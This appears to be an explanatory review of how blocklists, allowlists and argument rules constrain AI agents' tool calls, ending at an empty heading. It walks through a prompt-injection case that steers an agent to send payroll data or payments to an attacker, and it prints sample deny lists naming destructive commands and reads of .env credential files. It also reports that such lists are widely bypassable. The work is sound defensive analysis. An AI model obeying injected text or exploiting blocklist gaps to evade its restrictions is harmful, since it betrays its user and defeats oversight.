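# Blocklists, allowlists, range and regex constraints on AI agents' tool calls: what they stop, where they fail, and how their false positives are measured

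## How a rule decides on a tool call

A policy check is code that runs between an AI agent and its tools. Each time the agent asks to send an email, make a payment or run a command, the check compares the request with fixed rules, then allows it, blocks it, or escalates it to a person or a second model for a decision. Most rules are one of four types. A blocklist (many sources say "denylist") names tools, values or patterns to block and lets everything else through. An allowlist names what may pass, and the check blocks or escalates the rest. A range constraint sets a lower or upper bound on a number, date, length or count. A regex constraint requires a text argument to match, or not to match, a regular expression, a compact notation for a pattern of characters. Rules of every type stop some attacks, but they also block some legitimate calls, which are called false positives.

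The agents in question are programs built around a large language model (LLM). The model cannot send an email itself. It writes out a tool call, a request to run a named tool with given arguments; the software around the model runs the tool and hands the result back as text, and the model chooses its next step from that text. Take an office agent with four tools:

```
send_email(to, body)
pay(recipient, amount, currency)
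read_file(path)
run_command(command)
```

Suppose a user asks this agent to read the minutes in `/office/shared/minutes.txt` and email a summary to Alice. Someone has added a line to the minutes that says to forward the payroll file to eve@evil.example. The model receives both the user's request and the minutes as text, and nothing reliably marks the added line as content rather than an instruction, so its next tool call may well be an email to Eve. This is prompt injection, in which someone hides instructions in content the agent reads to make it act against its user.

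The example is simplified from one in *Progent* (Shi, He and colleagues, 2025), where the agent mails the user's whole inbox to an attacker and then posts the summary the user wanted. Because the user gets the summary, they have no particular reason to look further. *NOMOS* (2026), a paper on turning written policies into automatic checks, describes the same pattern for policy violations in general. The agent finishes the visible task but breaks the policy on the way, and the tool runs the offending call as normal. Shi and colleagues assume an honest user and an attacker who may control anything the tools return but cannot alter the model or its standing instructions. Under those assumptions, every call after the first tool result is suspect, even if it looks sensible.

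*From Alignment to Access Control* (2026) advises against enforcing a rule through a prompt wherever a hard mechanism is available, because a prompt guides the model but guarantees nothing. It calls instructions such as "never email strangers" "Pretty Please" enforcement. AWS's *Secure agent tool usage* lists the same mistake among common faults, because if only the agent's own reasoning limits its tool access, nothing outside the model stops a poisoned prompt.

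The tool call is a better place to intervene. As Shi and colleagues point out, all of an agent's effects on the outside world pass through tool calls. A call also has a fixed structure, a name and typed arguments, whereas the model's reasoning is free text, so ordinary code can compare the `to` argument with a list of addresses. Because no model is involved in that comparison, the same call checked against the same rules always gets the same verdict, however persuasive the injected text was. The check is also fast, taking microseconds in *NOMOS*. *NOMOS* also reimplemented PolicyGuard, an earlier system in which an LLM reads the whole dialogue before each call that changes something, and found that it added 74% to the average running time, with 347 extra model calls over 250 airline simulations.

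This makes the decisions consistent. *ToolGuardian* (2026) warns that "determinism is not the same as correctness", because executing a policy as a set of rules does not show that the policy is complete. If the office agent's rules misspell Alice's address, the check will block every email to her.

### Rules for the office agent

Progent is both the paper's title and the name of its system, and its rule language is a convenient one because it can express all four types. A small policy for the office agent might read:

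```
allow  send_email  when { to in ["alice@firm.example", "bob@firm.example"] }
allow  pay         when { 0 < amount and amount <= 500 and currency == "EUR" }
allow  read_file   when { path match "^/office/shared/[a-z0-9_]+\.txt$" }
forbid run_command when { command in ["shutdown now", "rm -rf /office"] }
allow  run_command when { true }
```

The `send_email` line is an allowlist of recipients. The `pay` line is a range constraint, with a condition on the currency because 500 euros and 500 yen are different payments. The `read_file` line is a regex constraint that requires the path to begin with `/office/shared/`, continue with lower-case letters, digits or underscores, and end in `.txt`. The last two lines together make a blocklist, which refuses two named commands and lets any other command run. The blocklist needs a line allowing the other commands because Progent blocks whatever no rule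 allows.

In full, a Progent rule has the form

$$E\;\; t \;\text{ when } \{\, e_1, e_2, \dots \,\}, \;\text{ fallback } f$$

where $E$ is either "allow" or "forbid", $t$ is the tool, and the $e_i$ are conditions on the tool's arguments, all of which must hold for the rule to apply. A condition can compare values, look for a value in a list, measure the length of an array or match a regular expression, and "and", "or" and "not" can join conditions together. The fallback $f$ replaces a call that the check blocks. It can stop the agent, hand the decision to the user, or return an error message. Shi and colleagues normally use the error message, which gives the reason for the refusal and asks the agent to try other tools or arguments and carry on with the user's task. *Sapien* (2026), a similar system, also returns its denials to the agent, on the ground that sending each one to the user makes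 the person do the enforcing.

When a call arrives, the procedure runs as follows.

1. Collect the rules that name the tool in the call.
2. Put the forbid rules ahead of the allow rules.
3. Go down the list, substituting the call's actual arguments into each rule's conditions, and stop at the first rule whose conditions all hold.
4. If that rule forbids, return its fallback instead of running the call. If it allows, run the call unchanged.
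5. If the list runs out, or no rule names the tool, block the call and return a default fallback.

Only one rule names `send_email`, and Alice is on its list, so the benign call `send_email(to="alice@firm.example", body=...)` goes through. The check applies the same rule to the injected call, `send_email(to="eve@evil.example", body=...)`. Eve is not on the list and there are no more rules to try, so step 5 blocks the call, even though no rule mentions her address. The agent gets an error message and can still send Alice her summary. Step 2 matters for a call like `run_command("shutdown now")`, which satisfies both `run_command` rules. The forbid rule comes first, so the check blocks the command.

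The whole procedure reduces to one condition. Write $e_R(v)$ for "the conditions of rule $R$ hold for the arguments $v$". Then the policy allows the call $t(v)$ exactly when

$$\big(\text{for every forbid rule } R \text{ on } t:\ \neg e_R(v)\big)\ \wedge\ \big(\text{for some allow rule } R' \text{ on } t:\ e_{R'}(v)\big).$$

The order of the rules therefore cannot change the verdict. At most, it changes which error message the agent sees when two forbid rules match the same call.

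In Progent, an LLM drafts the rules for each task from the user's request, before it has seen any text an attacker could have touched. It proposes changes as the agent learns more, but by then it may have read injected text. A solver, a program that decides questions of logic, therefore compares the new rules with the old. Any change that permits a new call needs approval, while other changes take effect immediately. The same rules always give the same verdict on a given call, but two runs of the same task may start with different rules.

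An organisation can also set fixed rules that take priority over the rules for each task. The check then applies the task's rules only where the fixed rules neither allow nor forbid the call. Shi and colleagues state that the calls that pass under this arrangement are a subset of those the fixed rules allow. That looks wrong as written, because a call that the fixed rules never mention runs if the task's rules allow it, although the fixed rules alone would have blocked it by default. The arrangement does provide a narrower guarantee that no task rule can allow a call that a fixed rule forbids.

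### Three lists, and the call that no rule mentions

Several coding agents, which edit a programmer's files and run shell commands, sort their rules into three lists: deny, ask and allow. An ask rule sends the call to the user for a decision. Anthropic says its coding agent, Claude Code, checks deny rules first, then ask rules, then allow rules. The first match decides, even if a later rule is more specific, so a deny rule for every `aws` command blocks `aws s3 ls` even if an allow rule names exactly that command.

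Products differ in whether an allow rule or an ask rule wins when both match. Docker's *Permissions*, which documents Docker's agent software, puts allow before ask. OpenAI's *Rules* describes an experimental feature that applies the most restrictive matching rule when the coding agent Codex wants to run a command outside its sandbox (a closed-off environment). If a user allows all `git` commands but adds an ask rule for `git push`, which publishes code, Claude Code and Codex will ask before a push. Docker's agent will push without asking, because the allow rule matches first. Deny beats allow in all three, so a user who moves rules between them will get the same refusals but may lose the prompts.

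A larger difference from Progent is the default decision for a call that no rule mentions. Progent blocks the call, while in the coding agents the decision depends on a setting. Anthropic's *permission modes* describes several such settings for Claude Code, and Docker has "safety modes" that rely on a label of safe, destructive or unknown for each call. *Agentao* (Jin, Jiao and Tong, 2026) describes a runtime for tool-using agents with a different default.

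| System and setting | A call that no rule mentions |
|---|---|
| Progent | The check blocks it |
| Claude Code, Manual | The user decides, except on read-only commands and some other harmless actions, which run |
| Claude Code, auto | A second model decides, except on reads and on most edits in the working directory |
| Claude Code, dontAsk | The check blocks whatever Manual mode would have asked about |
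| Claude Code, bypassPermissions | It runs, with a few exceptions |
| Docker, strict | The user decides |
| Docker, balanced | It runs if the label is "safe"; otherwise the user decides |
| Docker, restricted | It runs if the label is "safe"; otherwise the check blocks it |
| Docker, autonomous | It runs |
| Agentao | The user decides if the tool carries a "requires confirmation" mark; otherwise it runs, unless the agent is in read-only mode |

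Recent versions of Claude Code start interactive terminal sessions in auto mode. For many users, then, fixed rules decide the calls they cover and a second model decides much of the rest, so only some calls are guaranteed to get the same verdict each time they are made. Anthropic removes tool results from the requests Claude Code sends to this model, so that text in a hostile file cannot reach it directly, and says that auto mode does not guarantee safety.

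Jin and colleagues call the procedure in the Agentao row conservative and say that it refuses unknown tools and cases where authority is ambiguous. It is a little surprising, then, that the last line of the algorithm allows any known tool that lacks the confirmation mark. How conservative the procedure is depends largely on whoever set the marks. It is easy to write a policy that allows or denies by default without much thought. The draft Agent Policy Specification's *Tool Call Policy* gives a sample of each on one page, one that denies every tool except three and one that allows every call except a `write_file` outside a certain directory.

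### The four outcomes

A call is benign if it serves the user's task with the user's authority, and malicious if it serves an attacker. The check uses only the tool name and arguments, so it can allow or block calls of either kind. The office agent's policy can produce all four outcomes.

| | The check allows it | The check blocks it |
|---|---|---|
| Benign call | The summary goes to Alice | The user asks for an email to Carla, a new client who is not on the list |
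| Malicious call | `pay("Eve", 450, "EUR")`, which is within the range | The payroll email to Eve |

Carla's email is the false positive. Eve's payment is a miss because the `pay` rule limits the amount but not the recipient. For calls that nobody foresaw, blocking by default produces false positives on benign calls, while allowing by default lets malicious ones run. An escalated call belongs in none of the four cells until somebody answers the prompt, and that answer may be unreliable if approval fatigue leads the person to click "yes" out of habit.

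Whether a tool call is benign depends on the user's task. Shi and colleagues give the example of `send_email`, which is legitimate when the user wants to send Alice an update but a way to steal data when the user only wanted a summary of unread mail. They conclude that a policy loose enough for every task is too broad to stop attacks, and one written for a single task is too narrow for any other. They therefore argue for writing rules for each task. A fixed policy like the office agent's has to allow some attacks and block some legitimate calls.

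### Harm that the rules cannot see

Another condition on the recipient would stop Eve's payment. But some harmful calls have the same arguments as legitimate ones, so no condition on the arguments can distinguish them. Suppose the user asks the agent to choose a stationery supplier and pay for an order, and one supplier's web page contains hidden text that persuades the model to prefer it. The agent then pays 300 euros to a real supplier, as the task requires, and an honest comparison might have produced the same call.

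Shi and colleagues call this preference manipulation and place it outside Progent's scope, along with any other attack that stays within the privileges the task requires. They also left two such attacks out of all their experiments on AgentDojo, a benchmark of office, banking and travel tasks with injected instructions. In both, the injected text steers the agent towards a different but legitimate hotel. They argue that an attacker who controls the hotel listing could falsify it and fool a human too. That is reasonable, but it means that their attack success rates, the share of attacks that reach the attacker's goal, do not cover this kind of attack.

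Rules on tool calls also do not check what the agent tells the user. If the poisoned minutes lead the model to say that a supplier has changed its bank account, the user may log in and pay Eve personally. The agent has made no forbidden call, and the payment itself does not go through the agent's tools. Shi and colleagues leave such attacks to defences inside the model. False bank details can also appear in a tool argument. An email to Alice with those details in `body` satisfies the allowlist, because Alice is a permitted recipient and the rule does not check the email's content.

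## Blocklists: forbidding what is named

The office agent's blocklist names two commands, `shutdown now` and `rm -rf /office`. In general, a blocklist $L$ is a set of rules, each of which either matches a call $x$ or does not, and

$$L \text{ blocks } x \iff r(x) \text{ is true for at least one } r \in L.$$

Chen and Lin (2026), in *One Goal, Many Commands*, call this a purely negative specification. It lists what to reject, so it doesn't block anything left off the list. They also point out that a rule matches the form of a command, whereas the harm comes from what the command does when it runs. Whoever wrote the office policy presumably wanted to protect everything in `/office` from deletion, but the rule matches only one fourteen-character string.

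MITRE, a non-profit organisation, has included this failure in its public catalogue of software weaknesses since 2006, as entry 184, "Incomplete List of Disallowed Inputs". According to MITRE's *CWE-184*, developers tend to list the best-known bad inputs, often as a quick fix instead of repairing the underlying fault. Two of its examples come from AI software. In an agent platform, an incomplete list failed to stop attackers from injecting operating-system commands. In an API for generating text, the developers left out one of the characters that separate folders on Windows, which let attackers delete arbitrary files. MITRE also notes that common attacks may fail against such a list while minor variations succeed, so testing a blocklist with well-known attacks can make it look much more effective than it is.

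### When a list can be complete

A blocklist works if the developer can list every possible value. CodePath's *Prefer whitelisting over blacklisting* gives an example with six options, A to F, where only A, B and C are acceptable. Blocking D, E and F has the same result as allowing only the acceptable three. The two policies differ only when someone adds a dangerous option, Z, which the blocklist allows until someone notices.

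An agent's tool names can usually be listed in full. If an agent has six tools and its owner wants it never to use two of them, two rules are enough to block those tools, whatever the arguments. In Claude Code, according to Anthropic, a deny rule that consists only of a tool's name removes the tool from the model's context. A rule for a pattern within a tool, such as all `rm` commands, leaves the tool available and blocks matching calls when the model makes them. Claude Code can also warn the user at startup about most deny rules that name a non-existent tool, because it has a full list of tools, though not of commands, to check the rules against.

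Even a short list of tools can have gaps. Connecting the agent to an outside server may add new tools, though Claude Code accepts a wildcard rule that denies every tool from such servers in advance. Another tool may also have the same effect as the blocked one, so removing `send_email` from the office agent achieves little if `run_command` can start a mail program. Anthropic similarly warns that restricting Claude Code's web-fetching tool to certain sites does not cut off the rest of the internet while the agent can still run shell commands.

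Shell commands are much harder to list because a shell can run any program on the machine with any arguments, and each new package can add more programs. Google's documentation for its coding agent Gemini CLI, *Shell tool (`run_shell_command`)*, nevertheless includes a sample configuration that blocks `rm` and allows everything else. Gemini CLI compares the start of each command with the listed prefixes, splits chained commands to check each part, and blocks any command that matches both the blocklist and the allowlist. Google has since deprecated that setting and tells users to block commands through a more general policy engine. That engine's shorthands for shell rules match a prefix or a regular expression, so they still depend on how a command is written.

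*Blacklist defenses as a breeding ground for vulnerability variants* (Christey, 2006) describes what can happen when defenders keep extending a blocklist. An imaginary vendor wants to keep hostile scripts out of web pages. Over six patches the vendor keeps tightening its filter, and the attacker keeps finding a variant that passes. The seventh patch replaces the blocklist with a small set of permitted tags and attributes. Christey wrote this after David Litchfield had described the same sequence in a real Oracle product, and said the pattern recurred in all classes of software.

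### How complete real command lists are

Chen and Lin measured the problem in the blocklists people write for coding agents. They assume that an attacker has hijacked the agent, can choose its commands and has read the list. The last assumption is reasonable because many projects publish the list with their code. Chen and Lin also assume that the software matches every rule correctly, so any failure comes from what the list leaves out.

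One example comes from an open-source project that uses Claude Code. The asterisk stands for any text, and `.env` files hold settings that often include passwords and keys.

```
cat *.env*
head *.env*
tail *.env*
less *.env*
more *.env*
grep *.env*
```

All six commands print text from a file, so it is fairly clear what the project's developers were trying to prevent. But many other commands can do the same.

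To count such gaps, Chen and Lin need to say what a list is trying to block. They define an operation by the state in which it leaves the machine, so two quite different commands perform the same operation if, say, both put the file's contents on the screen. Write $P(c,a,o)$ for "command $c$ with arguments $a$ performs operation $o$" and $B(c,a)$ for "the list blocks $c$ with arguments $a$". A list blocks an operation at all if it blocks at least one way of performing it:

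$$\exists\, (c,a):\ P(c,a,o) \wedge B(c,a).$$

Given that, it fully blocks the operation if it blocks every way,

$$\forall\, (c,a):\ P(c,a,o) \Rightarrow B(c,a),$$

and incompletely blocks it if some way remains,

$$\exists\, (c,a):\ P(c,a,o) \wedge \neg B(c,a).$$

(Chen and Lin's printed formula for full blocking has a stray negation that contradicts their explanation.) The first condition keeps the count fair, up to a point. The list above does nothing to stop an agent from changing a file's owner, so it isn't counted as a failed attempt to prevent that.

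Their program, ShellSieve, looks for the remaining ways in four steps.

1. An LLM reads a command's documentation and proposes arguments with which that command alone, without any chaining, would perform one of seven file operations.
2. The program runs the proposal in a sandbox and examines the result. For reading, it plants a random token in a file and checks whether the token appears in the output. For deletion, it checks that the file has gone.
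3. If the proposal fails, the LLM sees the error messages and may try again, up to five times.
4. The program does the same for the commands on each blocklist, then compares what the listed commands do with what the unlisted ones do.

The evaluation counts a bypass only if it ran and had the forbidden effect, so mistakes by the LLM can lead to missed bypasses but not false ones. The whole evaluation took three hours and cost $25 in model use, so an attacker could afford it too.

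The dataset contains 1,709 blocklists from GitHub with 13,332 rules, or about eight rules per list. (The paper's introduction once gives 1,731 lists, but its dataset table adds up to 1,709.) It includes 1,000 lists for Claude Code, randomly sampled from 24,453 repositories, as well as 573 for OpenCode and 136 for Codex. Most belong to small projects, with 1,629 coming from repositories with fewer than 100 stars, GitHub's measure of popularity.

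Of the lists that block a given operation at all, 69.0% to 98.6% block it incompletely, depending on the operation. The rates stay above 46.2% for each of the three agents. The most popular projects have the lowest rates for four of the seven operations, but that group contains only eleven lists, so one list can change the group's rate by nine percentage points or more.

Professionally maintained blocklists can also miss dangerous commands. Claude Code's auto mode has a built-in list of commands that can run arbitrary code, such as language interpreters and shells. The list sends these commands to a second model rather than blocking them, and prevents a user's allow rule from approving them silently. Chen and Lin found that it omitted a utility that can also run arbitrary code and is present on every Unix-like system, and they reported this to Anthropic.

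They then counted how many more commands an incomplete list would have to block to prevent each operation on a standard Debian Linux system.

| Operation | Fewest | Mean | Most |
|---|---|---|---|
| Read a file | 200 | 217 | 222 |
| Write to a file | 5 | 97 | 106 |
| Create a file | 63 | 98 | 180 |
| Delete a file | 38 | 54 | 58 |
| Copy a file | 27 | 39 | 40 |
| Change a file's mode (its access permissions) | 1 | 3 | 13 |
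| Change a file's owner or group | 7 | 11 | 12 |

Whether a blocklist can work on shell commands depends a good deal on which operation it is meant to block. Many programs read files, but few need to change access permissions. Somebody could plausibly find and add three missing commands that change permissions, but hardly anyone will add 217 that read files, and the next package installed may bring another.

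The exact counts deserve some caution. Elsewhere in the paper, Chen and Lin compare commands that perform one operation with those that perform several, and the two groups total only 144. It is hard to see how reading alone could then require 217 more. Perhaps the larger figure counts different ways of invoking the same program, in which case one broad rule could close several gaps. The contrast between reading and changing permissions would probably hold after a recount, but 217 may not be the number of programs a defender has to find.

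### Why the gaps are there

Chen and Lin test three explanations for why blocklists miss commands and accept two. The first is ignorance: blocklist authors do not list commands they have never heard of. Chen and Lin estimate familiarity from each command's rank in the Debian Popularity Contest, a survey of the software Debian users have installed, and find that less popular commands are more likely to be bypasses. They report both that popularity carries essentially no signal for deletion and that the trend holds for all seven operations, so it is unclear whether deletion is an exception.

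The test is weaker than it looks because it counts a command as a bypass if it gets past any one list. With so many lists and so few rules in each, almost any command that can perform an operation will get past at least one. The trend may therefore partly reflect that less popular programs on a Debian system can more often read or write files, which has little to do with what the people who write blocklists know. Their ignorance is still a likely cause, since few people could name two hundred ways to print a file.

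The second explanation is that some commands do several things, and a list's author may leave one of them off because the agent needs it for ordinary work. The 35 commands that perform more than one operation bypass a median of 664 lists each, against 281 for the 109 commands that perform only one. The difference is statistically significant ($p = 0.006$), but the effect is small on the scale that Chen and Lin quote (Cliff's $\delta = 0.30$, where $\delta$ runs from −1 to 1 and is 0 when neither group tends to have higher values). They also pool the counts over all seven operations, so a command that performs three of them has three chances to get past each list. The result shows that versatile commands tend to account for more bypasses each than single-purpose ones, but not that anyone left them off the lists deliberately.

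Chen and Lin conclude that most of the commands blocklist authors miss have their dangerous abilities openly documented. They reject the explanation that these abilities are so hidden that an author who knows the command would never connect it with the operation. They checked short community-written help pages that list each command's most common uses. Among commands whose page mentions reading files, 45.0% can be used to bypass a block on reading, compared with 15.3% of commands whose page does not. Across all operations, the figures are 40.1% and 5.7%.

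That does not follow, because the two groups may differ greatly in size. Suppose the help pages of 100 commands mention reading and those of 1,000 do not. At the reported rates, the first group contains 45 bypasses and the second 153, so most bypasses would be in commands whose help pages don't mention reading. The first group's higher rate is also unsurprising, since commands that advertise reading files can usually read them. A better test would include only commands that can perform the operation and measure whether authors omit the less obvious ones more often. Abilities that help pages don't mention may well matter, and this comparison cannot rule that out.

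### What it costs to close a gap

If versatility is even part of the explanation, a blocklist's gaps and its false positives are connected. Blocking an obscure program that nobody on the project uses stops no legitimate calls, but people use versatile programs, so a rule against one blocks their calls as well as the attacker's. If 30 of every 1,000 benign calls use the command, and no earlier rule blocks them, the new rule raises the false-positive rate by three percentage points.

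A language interpreter such as Python can read, write or delete anything its user can, so a blocklist that permits it blocks very little. But blocking Python would stop a coding agent from running a Python project's tests. This is presumably why Claude Code's built-in list sends interpreters to a second model for a decision instead of refusing them outright.

A rule can try to block only the harmful uses of a command by matching its arguments. Anthropic calls such patterns fragile because they can miss the same request when its options are in a different order or its address is in a variable. Claude Code also can't block a command broadly and then make exceptions for harmless uses, because deny rules always override allow rules. Leaving out a space can make a rule too broad, since `ls*` also matches the unrelated program `lsof`, while `ls *` does not.

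Chen and Lin did not measure false positives, either for the lists as they stand or for the lists with every gap closed. They assume that people who write blocklists keep them short to avoid blocking benign work, which is plausible but untested. *SkillGate* (2026), a paper on detecting malicious "skills" (files that extend what a coding agent can do), provides some indirect evidence on false positives. Two static scanners, which inspect a file without running it, flagged 17.4% and 50.4% of 1,500 benign skill files. These figures do not transfer directly, because they are for files rather than tool calls and a scanner may flag a file at a severity too low to block it. They do suggest that broad rules for finding suspicious content can produce many false positives.

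### How far the measurements reach

The main weakness in the figures of 69.0% to 98.6% is that Chen and Lin infer what a list's author wanted from what the list blocks. This seems right for the six rules about `.env` files but is less convincing for a rule against a language interpreter. Their method treats such a rule as an attempt to block file creation, deletion and whatever else the interpreter can do, so it counts the list as incomplete because other programs can create files. The list's author may only have wanted to stop the agent from running untested scripts.

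Chen and Lin describe their rates as lower bounds because a more thorough search would find more bypasses. This holds if one accepts their definition of each list's purpose. If that definition includes aims the list's writers never had, the share of lists that fail at their real purpose could be lower than the reported rate.

All seven operations involve files. The study leaves out network operations, such as sending stolen data to an outside server, because testing them would have required simulated servers. The payroll email to Eve is an attack of that kind, so the study did not measure how often a blocklist would stop its shell equivalent.

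Also, a command that gets past the blocklist does not necessarily run. In a system with three lists, a command that no rule mentions goes to the user or a second model. Chen and Lin reply that users approve 93% of requests, so asking is nearly the same as allowing. But if most requests are harmless, a careful reviewer would approve most of them too. Measuring how much protection the prompt adds would require the approval rate for harmful commands. The objection that a bypass may not run is weaker where a user has set the agent to run unlisted commands without asking, as with the office agent.

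### What blocklists are good for

A blocklist of eight lines takes a few minutes to write, and anyone who knows the commands can see what it forbids. It also interrupts little ordinary work if its entries are narrow. *Progent*'s policy for the office agent could forbid two commands without listing every other command the agent might need, which is the main work in writing an allowlist. *Parallax* (2026), which describes a layered system for checking agents' actions, offers some evidence that simple checks need not be disruptive. In its small test on legitimate development work, the first tier and the heuristic engine blocked nothing, and the false positives came from a trained classifier and a later evaluator. The test is too small to establish that the simple checks' true false-positive rate is near zero, and narrow rules avoid false positives partly by matching very little.

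Blocklists work best against accidents, because an agent that makes a mistake will probably write the command in its most common form, while an attacker looks for a form the list does not cover. Anthropic says its own deny rules cover the form that Claude usually produces and are not "a security boundary". It recommends a sandbox for file and network restrictions that do not depend on the text of a command.

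Even without an attacker, an agent may get round the list, especially as Progent's usual error message includes an instruction to try another way. If the task is to free disk space and the check refuses one deletion command, a capable model may choose another, and Chen and Lin count dozens. An error message stating the forbidden effect, such as deleting anything in `/office`, would probably help, but the protection would then depend again on the model following an instruction.

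Blocklists can also detect suspicious activity. MITRE advises developers to use them only for this purpose, and to rely on other mechanisms, such as allowlists, for protection. If an agent assigned to summarise minutes tries to run `rm -rf /office`, the attempt is worth investigating even though the blocklist stopped it, because the next attempt may take a form that is not on the list.

The code editor Cursor replaced its blocklist with allowlists in version 1.3 for commands that run without approval. Its release notes, *Shared terminal with Agent, context usage in chat, and faster edits*, describe the change as a security improvement. Other products keep both kinds of list, so a user can allow `git` commands in general and block `git push`. The blocklist then only has to cover the ways of publishing code with `git`, but Anthropic notes that a rule against `git push` still misses the same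 push written in another form.

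## Allowlists: permitting only what is named

An allowlist $A$ is also a set of rules, but here a match lets the call through:

$$A \text{ allows } x \iff r(x) \text{ is true for at least one } r \in A.$$

An allowlist that is missing an entry blocks a legitimate call, such as the email to Carla, rather than letting a harmful one through as an incomplete blocklist would. An attack can still get past an allowlist, but only through an entry that is too broad.

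Saltzer and Schroeder argued for this arrangement in a 1975 paper on protecting information in computer systems. Their principle of "fail-safe defaults", quoted in Shostack + Friends Blog's *Friday Star Wars*, is to base access on permission rather than exclusion. They credit E. Glaser with suggesting it in 1965. They reasoned that designers of a large system will overlook something, and that it is safer if nobody can reach what they overlooked. They also argued that mistakes that deny access are easier to notice. People who can't open a file they need will complain, but a file that is open to everyone can stay that way for years, because ordinary users don't try to read things they shouldn't.

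The second reason applies only partly to agents. When a check blocks an agent's call, the agent may try another tool, or skip the step and report that it has finished. The user may never learn of the mistake, so somebody has to monitor the refusals. AWS's *AGENTSEC02-BP02 Validate tool inputs and outputs* recommends an alarm on the rate of failed checks, since a rise may mean an attack or a badly configured rule.

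### Tools, values and tasks

The coarsest allowlist names only tools. If the office agent's list contains only `read_file` and `send_email`, the agent cannot pay anyone or run a command, even if an injected instruction tells it to. This holds as long as every call goes through the check.

A finer allowlist also names the permitted values of an argument, like the two addresses in the office agent's `send_email` rule. AWS recommends value lists for fields with a closed set of values, which would suit the `currency` argument of `pay`. A strict setting in its Bedrock service applies the list while the model writes the call, so the model cannot produce an unlisted value. That works well for currencies but could be risky for recipients. If a model has started an email to Carla but can only write Alice's or Bob's address, it might send the email to one of them. A check that runs after the call is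 written would reject Carla's address and return an error.

Argument names need an allowlist too. AWS advises developers to refuse any argument that the tool's definition does not include. The argument names in the rules are also worth checking against that definition, because a misspelled name may leave the real argument unrestricted.

Lists of either kind can be permanent, or an LLM can write them for a single task, as in Progent. A list written for summarising minutes could permit the office agent one file, one recipient and no payments. The LLM has to predict which calls the task will need, and its errors either block legitimate calls (false positives) or permit calls an attacker could exploit.

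### A permitted tool with a harmful argument

The main weakness of a tool list is that it ignores arguments. The office agent needs `send_email` to send Alice her summary, so a tool list has to permit it, which also permits the payroll email to Eve. *Sapien*, published by researchers at Google and the University of Massachusetts Amherst in October 2026, gives a harder example, in which a user asks an agent to refund whoever sent her money last week. The tightest possible tool list permits reading the transactions and sending money, which is enough to send any amount to anyone. A value list written in advance doesn't solve the problem, because the right recipient and amount only become known when the agent reads the transactions.

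Sapien's rules can therefore refer to what has already happened in the task. For the refund, they could require the agent to read the transactions first, then pay only a sender and an amount that appear in them. Calls are still refused by default, but the allowlist now consists of permitted sequences of calls instead of single calls.

The researchers compared these rules with tool lists that an LLM wrote for each task. They paired each of the 97 tasks in AgentDojo with every attack goal from the same group of tasks, which gave 949 attack instances. They also wrote 212 attack instances for Toolathlon, a benchmark of 108 longer tasks with more than 600 tools. The first column below lists the model that wrote the rules.

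| Model and benchmark | Attacks blocked by a tool list | Attacks blocked by Sapien's rules |
|---|---|---|
| Gemini 3.8 Flash, AgentDojo | 86.4% | 93.4% |
| Claude Opus 5, AgentDojo | 85.8% | 94.8% |
| Claude Sonnet 5, AgentDojo | 86.8% | 95.2% |
| Gemini 3.1 Pro, AgentDojo | 82.7% | 93.2% |
| Gemini 3.8 Flash, Toolathlon | 32.4% | 64.6% |

These rates are analytical. The researchers assumed that the attacker already controlled the agent and could make it propose any call, then checked whether the rules permitted any sequence of calls that reached the attacker's goal. They did not plant injections and count how often the agent obeyed them.

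1. If the rules forbid a tool that the attack cannot do without, the attack fails.
2. If the rules permit the benchmark's own example of the attack, which AgentDojo supplies, the attack succeeds.
3. Otherwise a second agent reads the rules and searches for a permitted sequence that reaches the goal. If it finds one, the attack succeeds.
4. The researchers judge any remaining instances by hand.

They also assumed the attacker could fool any LLM that reads hostile text while the task is running. They trusted only the model calls that write rules from clean input.

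A rate of 86.4% therefore means that for 86.4% of the pairs of task and goal, the rules make the attack impossible even if the model obeys every injected word. For the other 13.6%, the outcome depends on whether the model resists, so the rate is not the share of attacks that would fail in practice. This test is stricter than a live one, and the rate does not improve when the model gets better at ignoring injections. The rate still depends on human judgement in the first and last steps. If the researchers overlooked another way to reach a goal without the forbidden tool, they counted a possible attack as blocked.

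On AgentDojo, Sapien's rules let through between a half and two-thirds fewer attacks than the tool lists did. The tool lists still blocked 82.7% to 86.8% of attacks, in large part because attack goals were paired with user tasks at random. A random goal often needs a tool that the user's task doesn't, in which case even the coarsest list blocks it. On Toolathlon, the researchers chose goals that used the task's own tools and data, and the tool lists blocked only about a third. An attacker who knows what the agent is for would choose goals the same way, so the Toolathlon figure is probably the better guide to a targeted attack.

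On AgentDojo, 82.1% of the attacks that Sapien's rules let through depended on the meaning of some text, usually because the harm was in a message body, a file's contents or the agent's final answer. One attack goal, which only asks the agent to output a certain sentence, accounted for 36% of the successful attacks, and no rule on tool calls could have stopped it. Another 16.1% of the attacks that got through used read-only tools, which the rules often leave unrestricted so that the agent can gather information. This lets an attacker send the agent to a web address of their choice.

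The protection an allowlist gives also depends on how narrow the permitted tools are. Permitting a tool that runs arbitrary Python code weakens an allowlist as much as it weakens a blocklist. The researchers removed such a tool from Toolathlon for every agent they compared, and required Sapien's rules to restrict which shell commands could run. An organisation whose agents need a general code tool will probably get worse results than the table shows.

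### The cost in unfinished tasks

A list that permits nothing would block every attack, so the rates above mean little unless the effect on legitimate work is also measured. On AgentDojo, agents with tool lists completed up to two fewer of the 97 tasks than agents with no rules, depending on the model. Agents with Sapien's rules completed one to five fewer. On a 20-task sample of Toolathlon, run once with each of the four models, agents with Sapien's rules completed 43 of 80 runs and unrestricted agents completed 45. Differences of one or two tasks could easily be chance with numbers this small.

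On Toolathlon, an allowlist that named only tools got in the agent's way more than rules that also restricted arguments. *Sapien* attributes this partly to the LLM that writes the tool list having to either permit `send_email` with any arguments for the whole task or withhold it. In one AgentDojo task, the user asked the agent to carry out a to-do list that had arrived by email. The LLM withheld `send_email` because the user had not asked for any emails, and the task failed when the to-do list called for a reply. Sapien's rules could permit the tool safely because they restricted its arguments, allowing an email only to the list's sender, and only after the agent had read the list.

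Most of Sapien's false positives came from wrong guesses about data. A rule written from the user's words required "London Luxury Hotel", but the hotel was listed in the database as "London Luxury", so the check blocked a correct call. Someone writing a value list by hand could easily make the same mistake.

The number of blocked calls is a poor measure of how much tool lists interfere with an agent's tasks. Across 388 AgentDojo runs, the tool lists blocked one call. The agent could see the list in its instructions, so when a tool it needed was missing, it usually gave up without trying the call. Sapien's rules blocked 54 calls in the same number of runs, and 11 of the 20 tasks with a blocked call failed. An operator who read only the log of refusals would conclude that the tool lists had barely interfered, even in the to-do task that failed.

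Writing the rules also takes time. On AgentDojo, writing a tool list took 18 to 23 seconds per task and writing Sapien's rules took 43 to 100 seconds, while the deterministic checks took less than a millisecond per step. The delay from writing rules matters less on a ten-minute task than on a thirty-second one.

### Progent against live attacks

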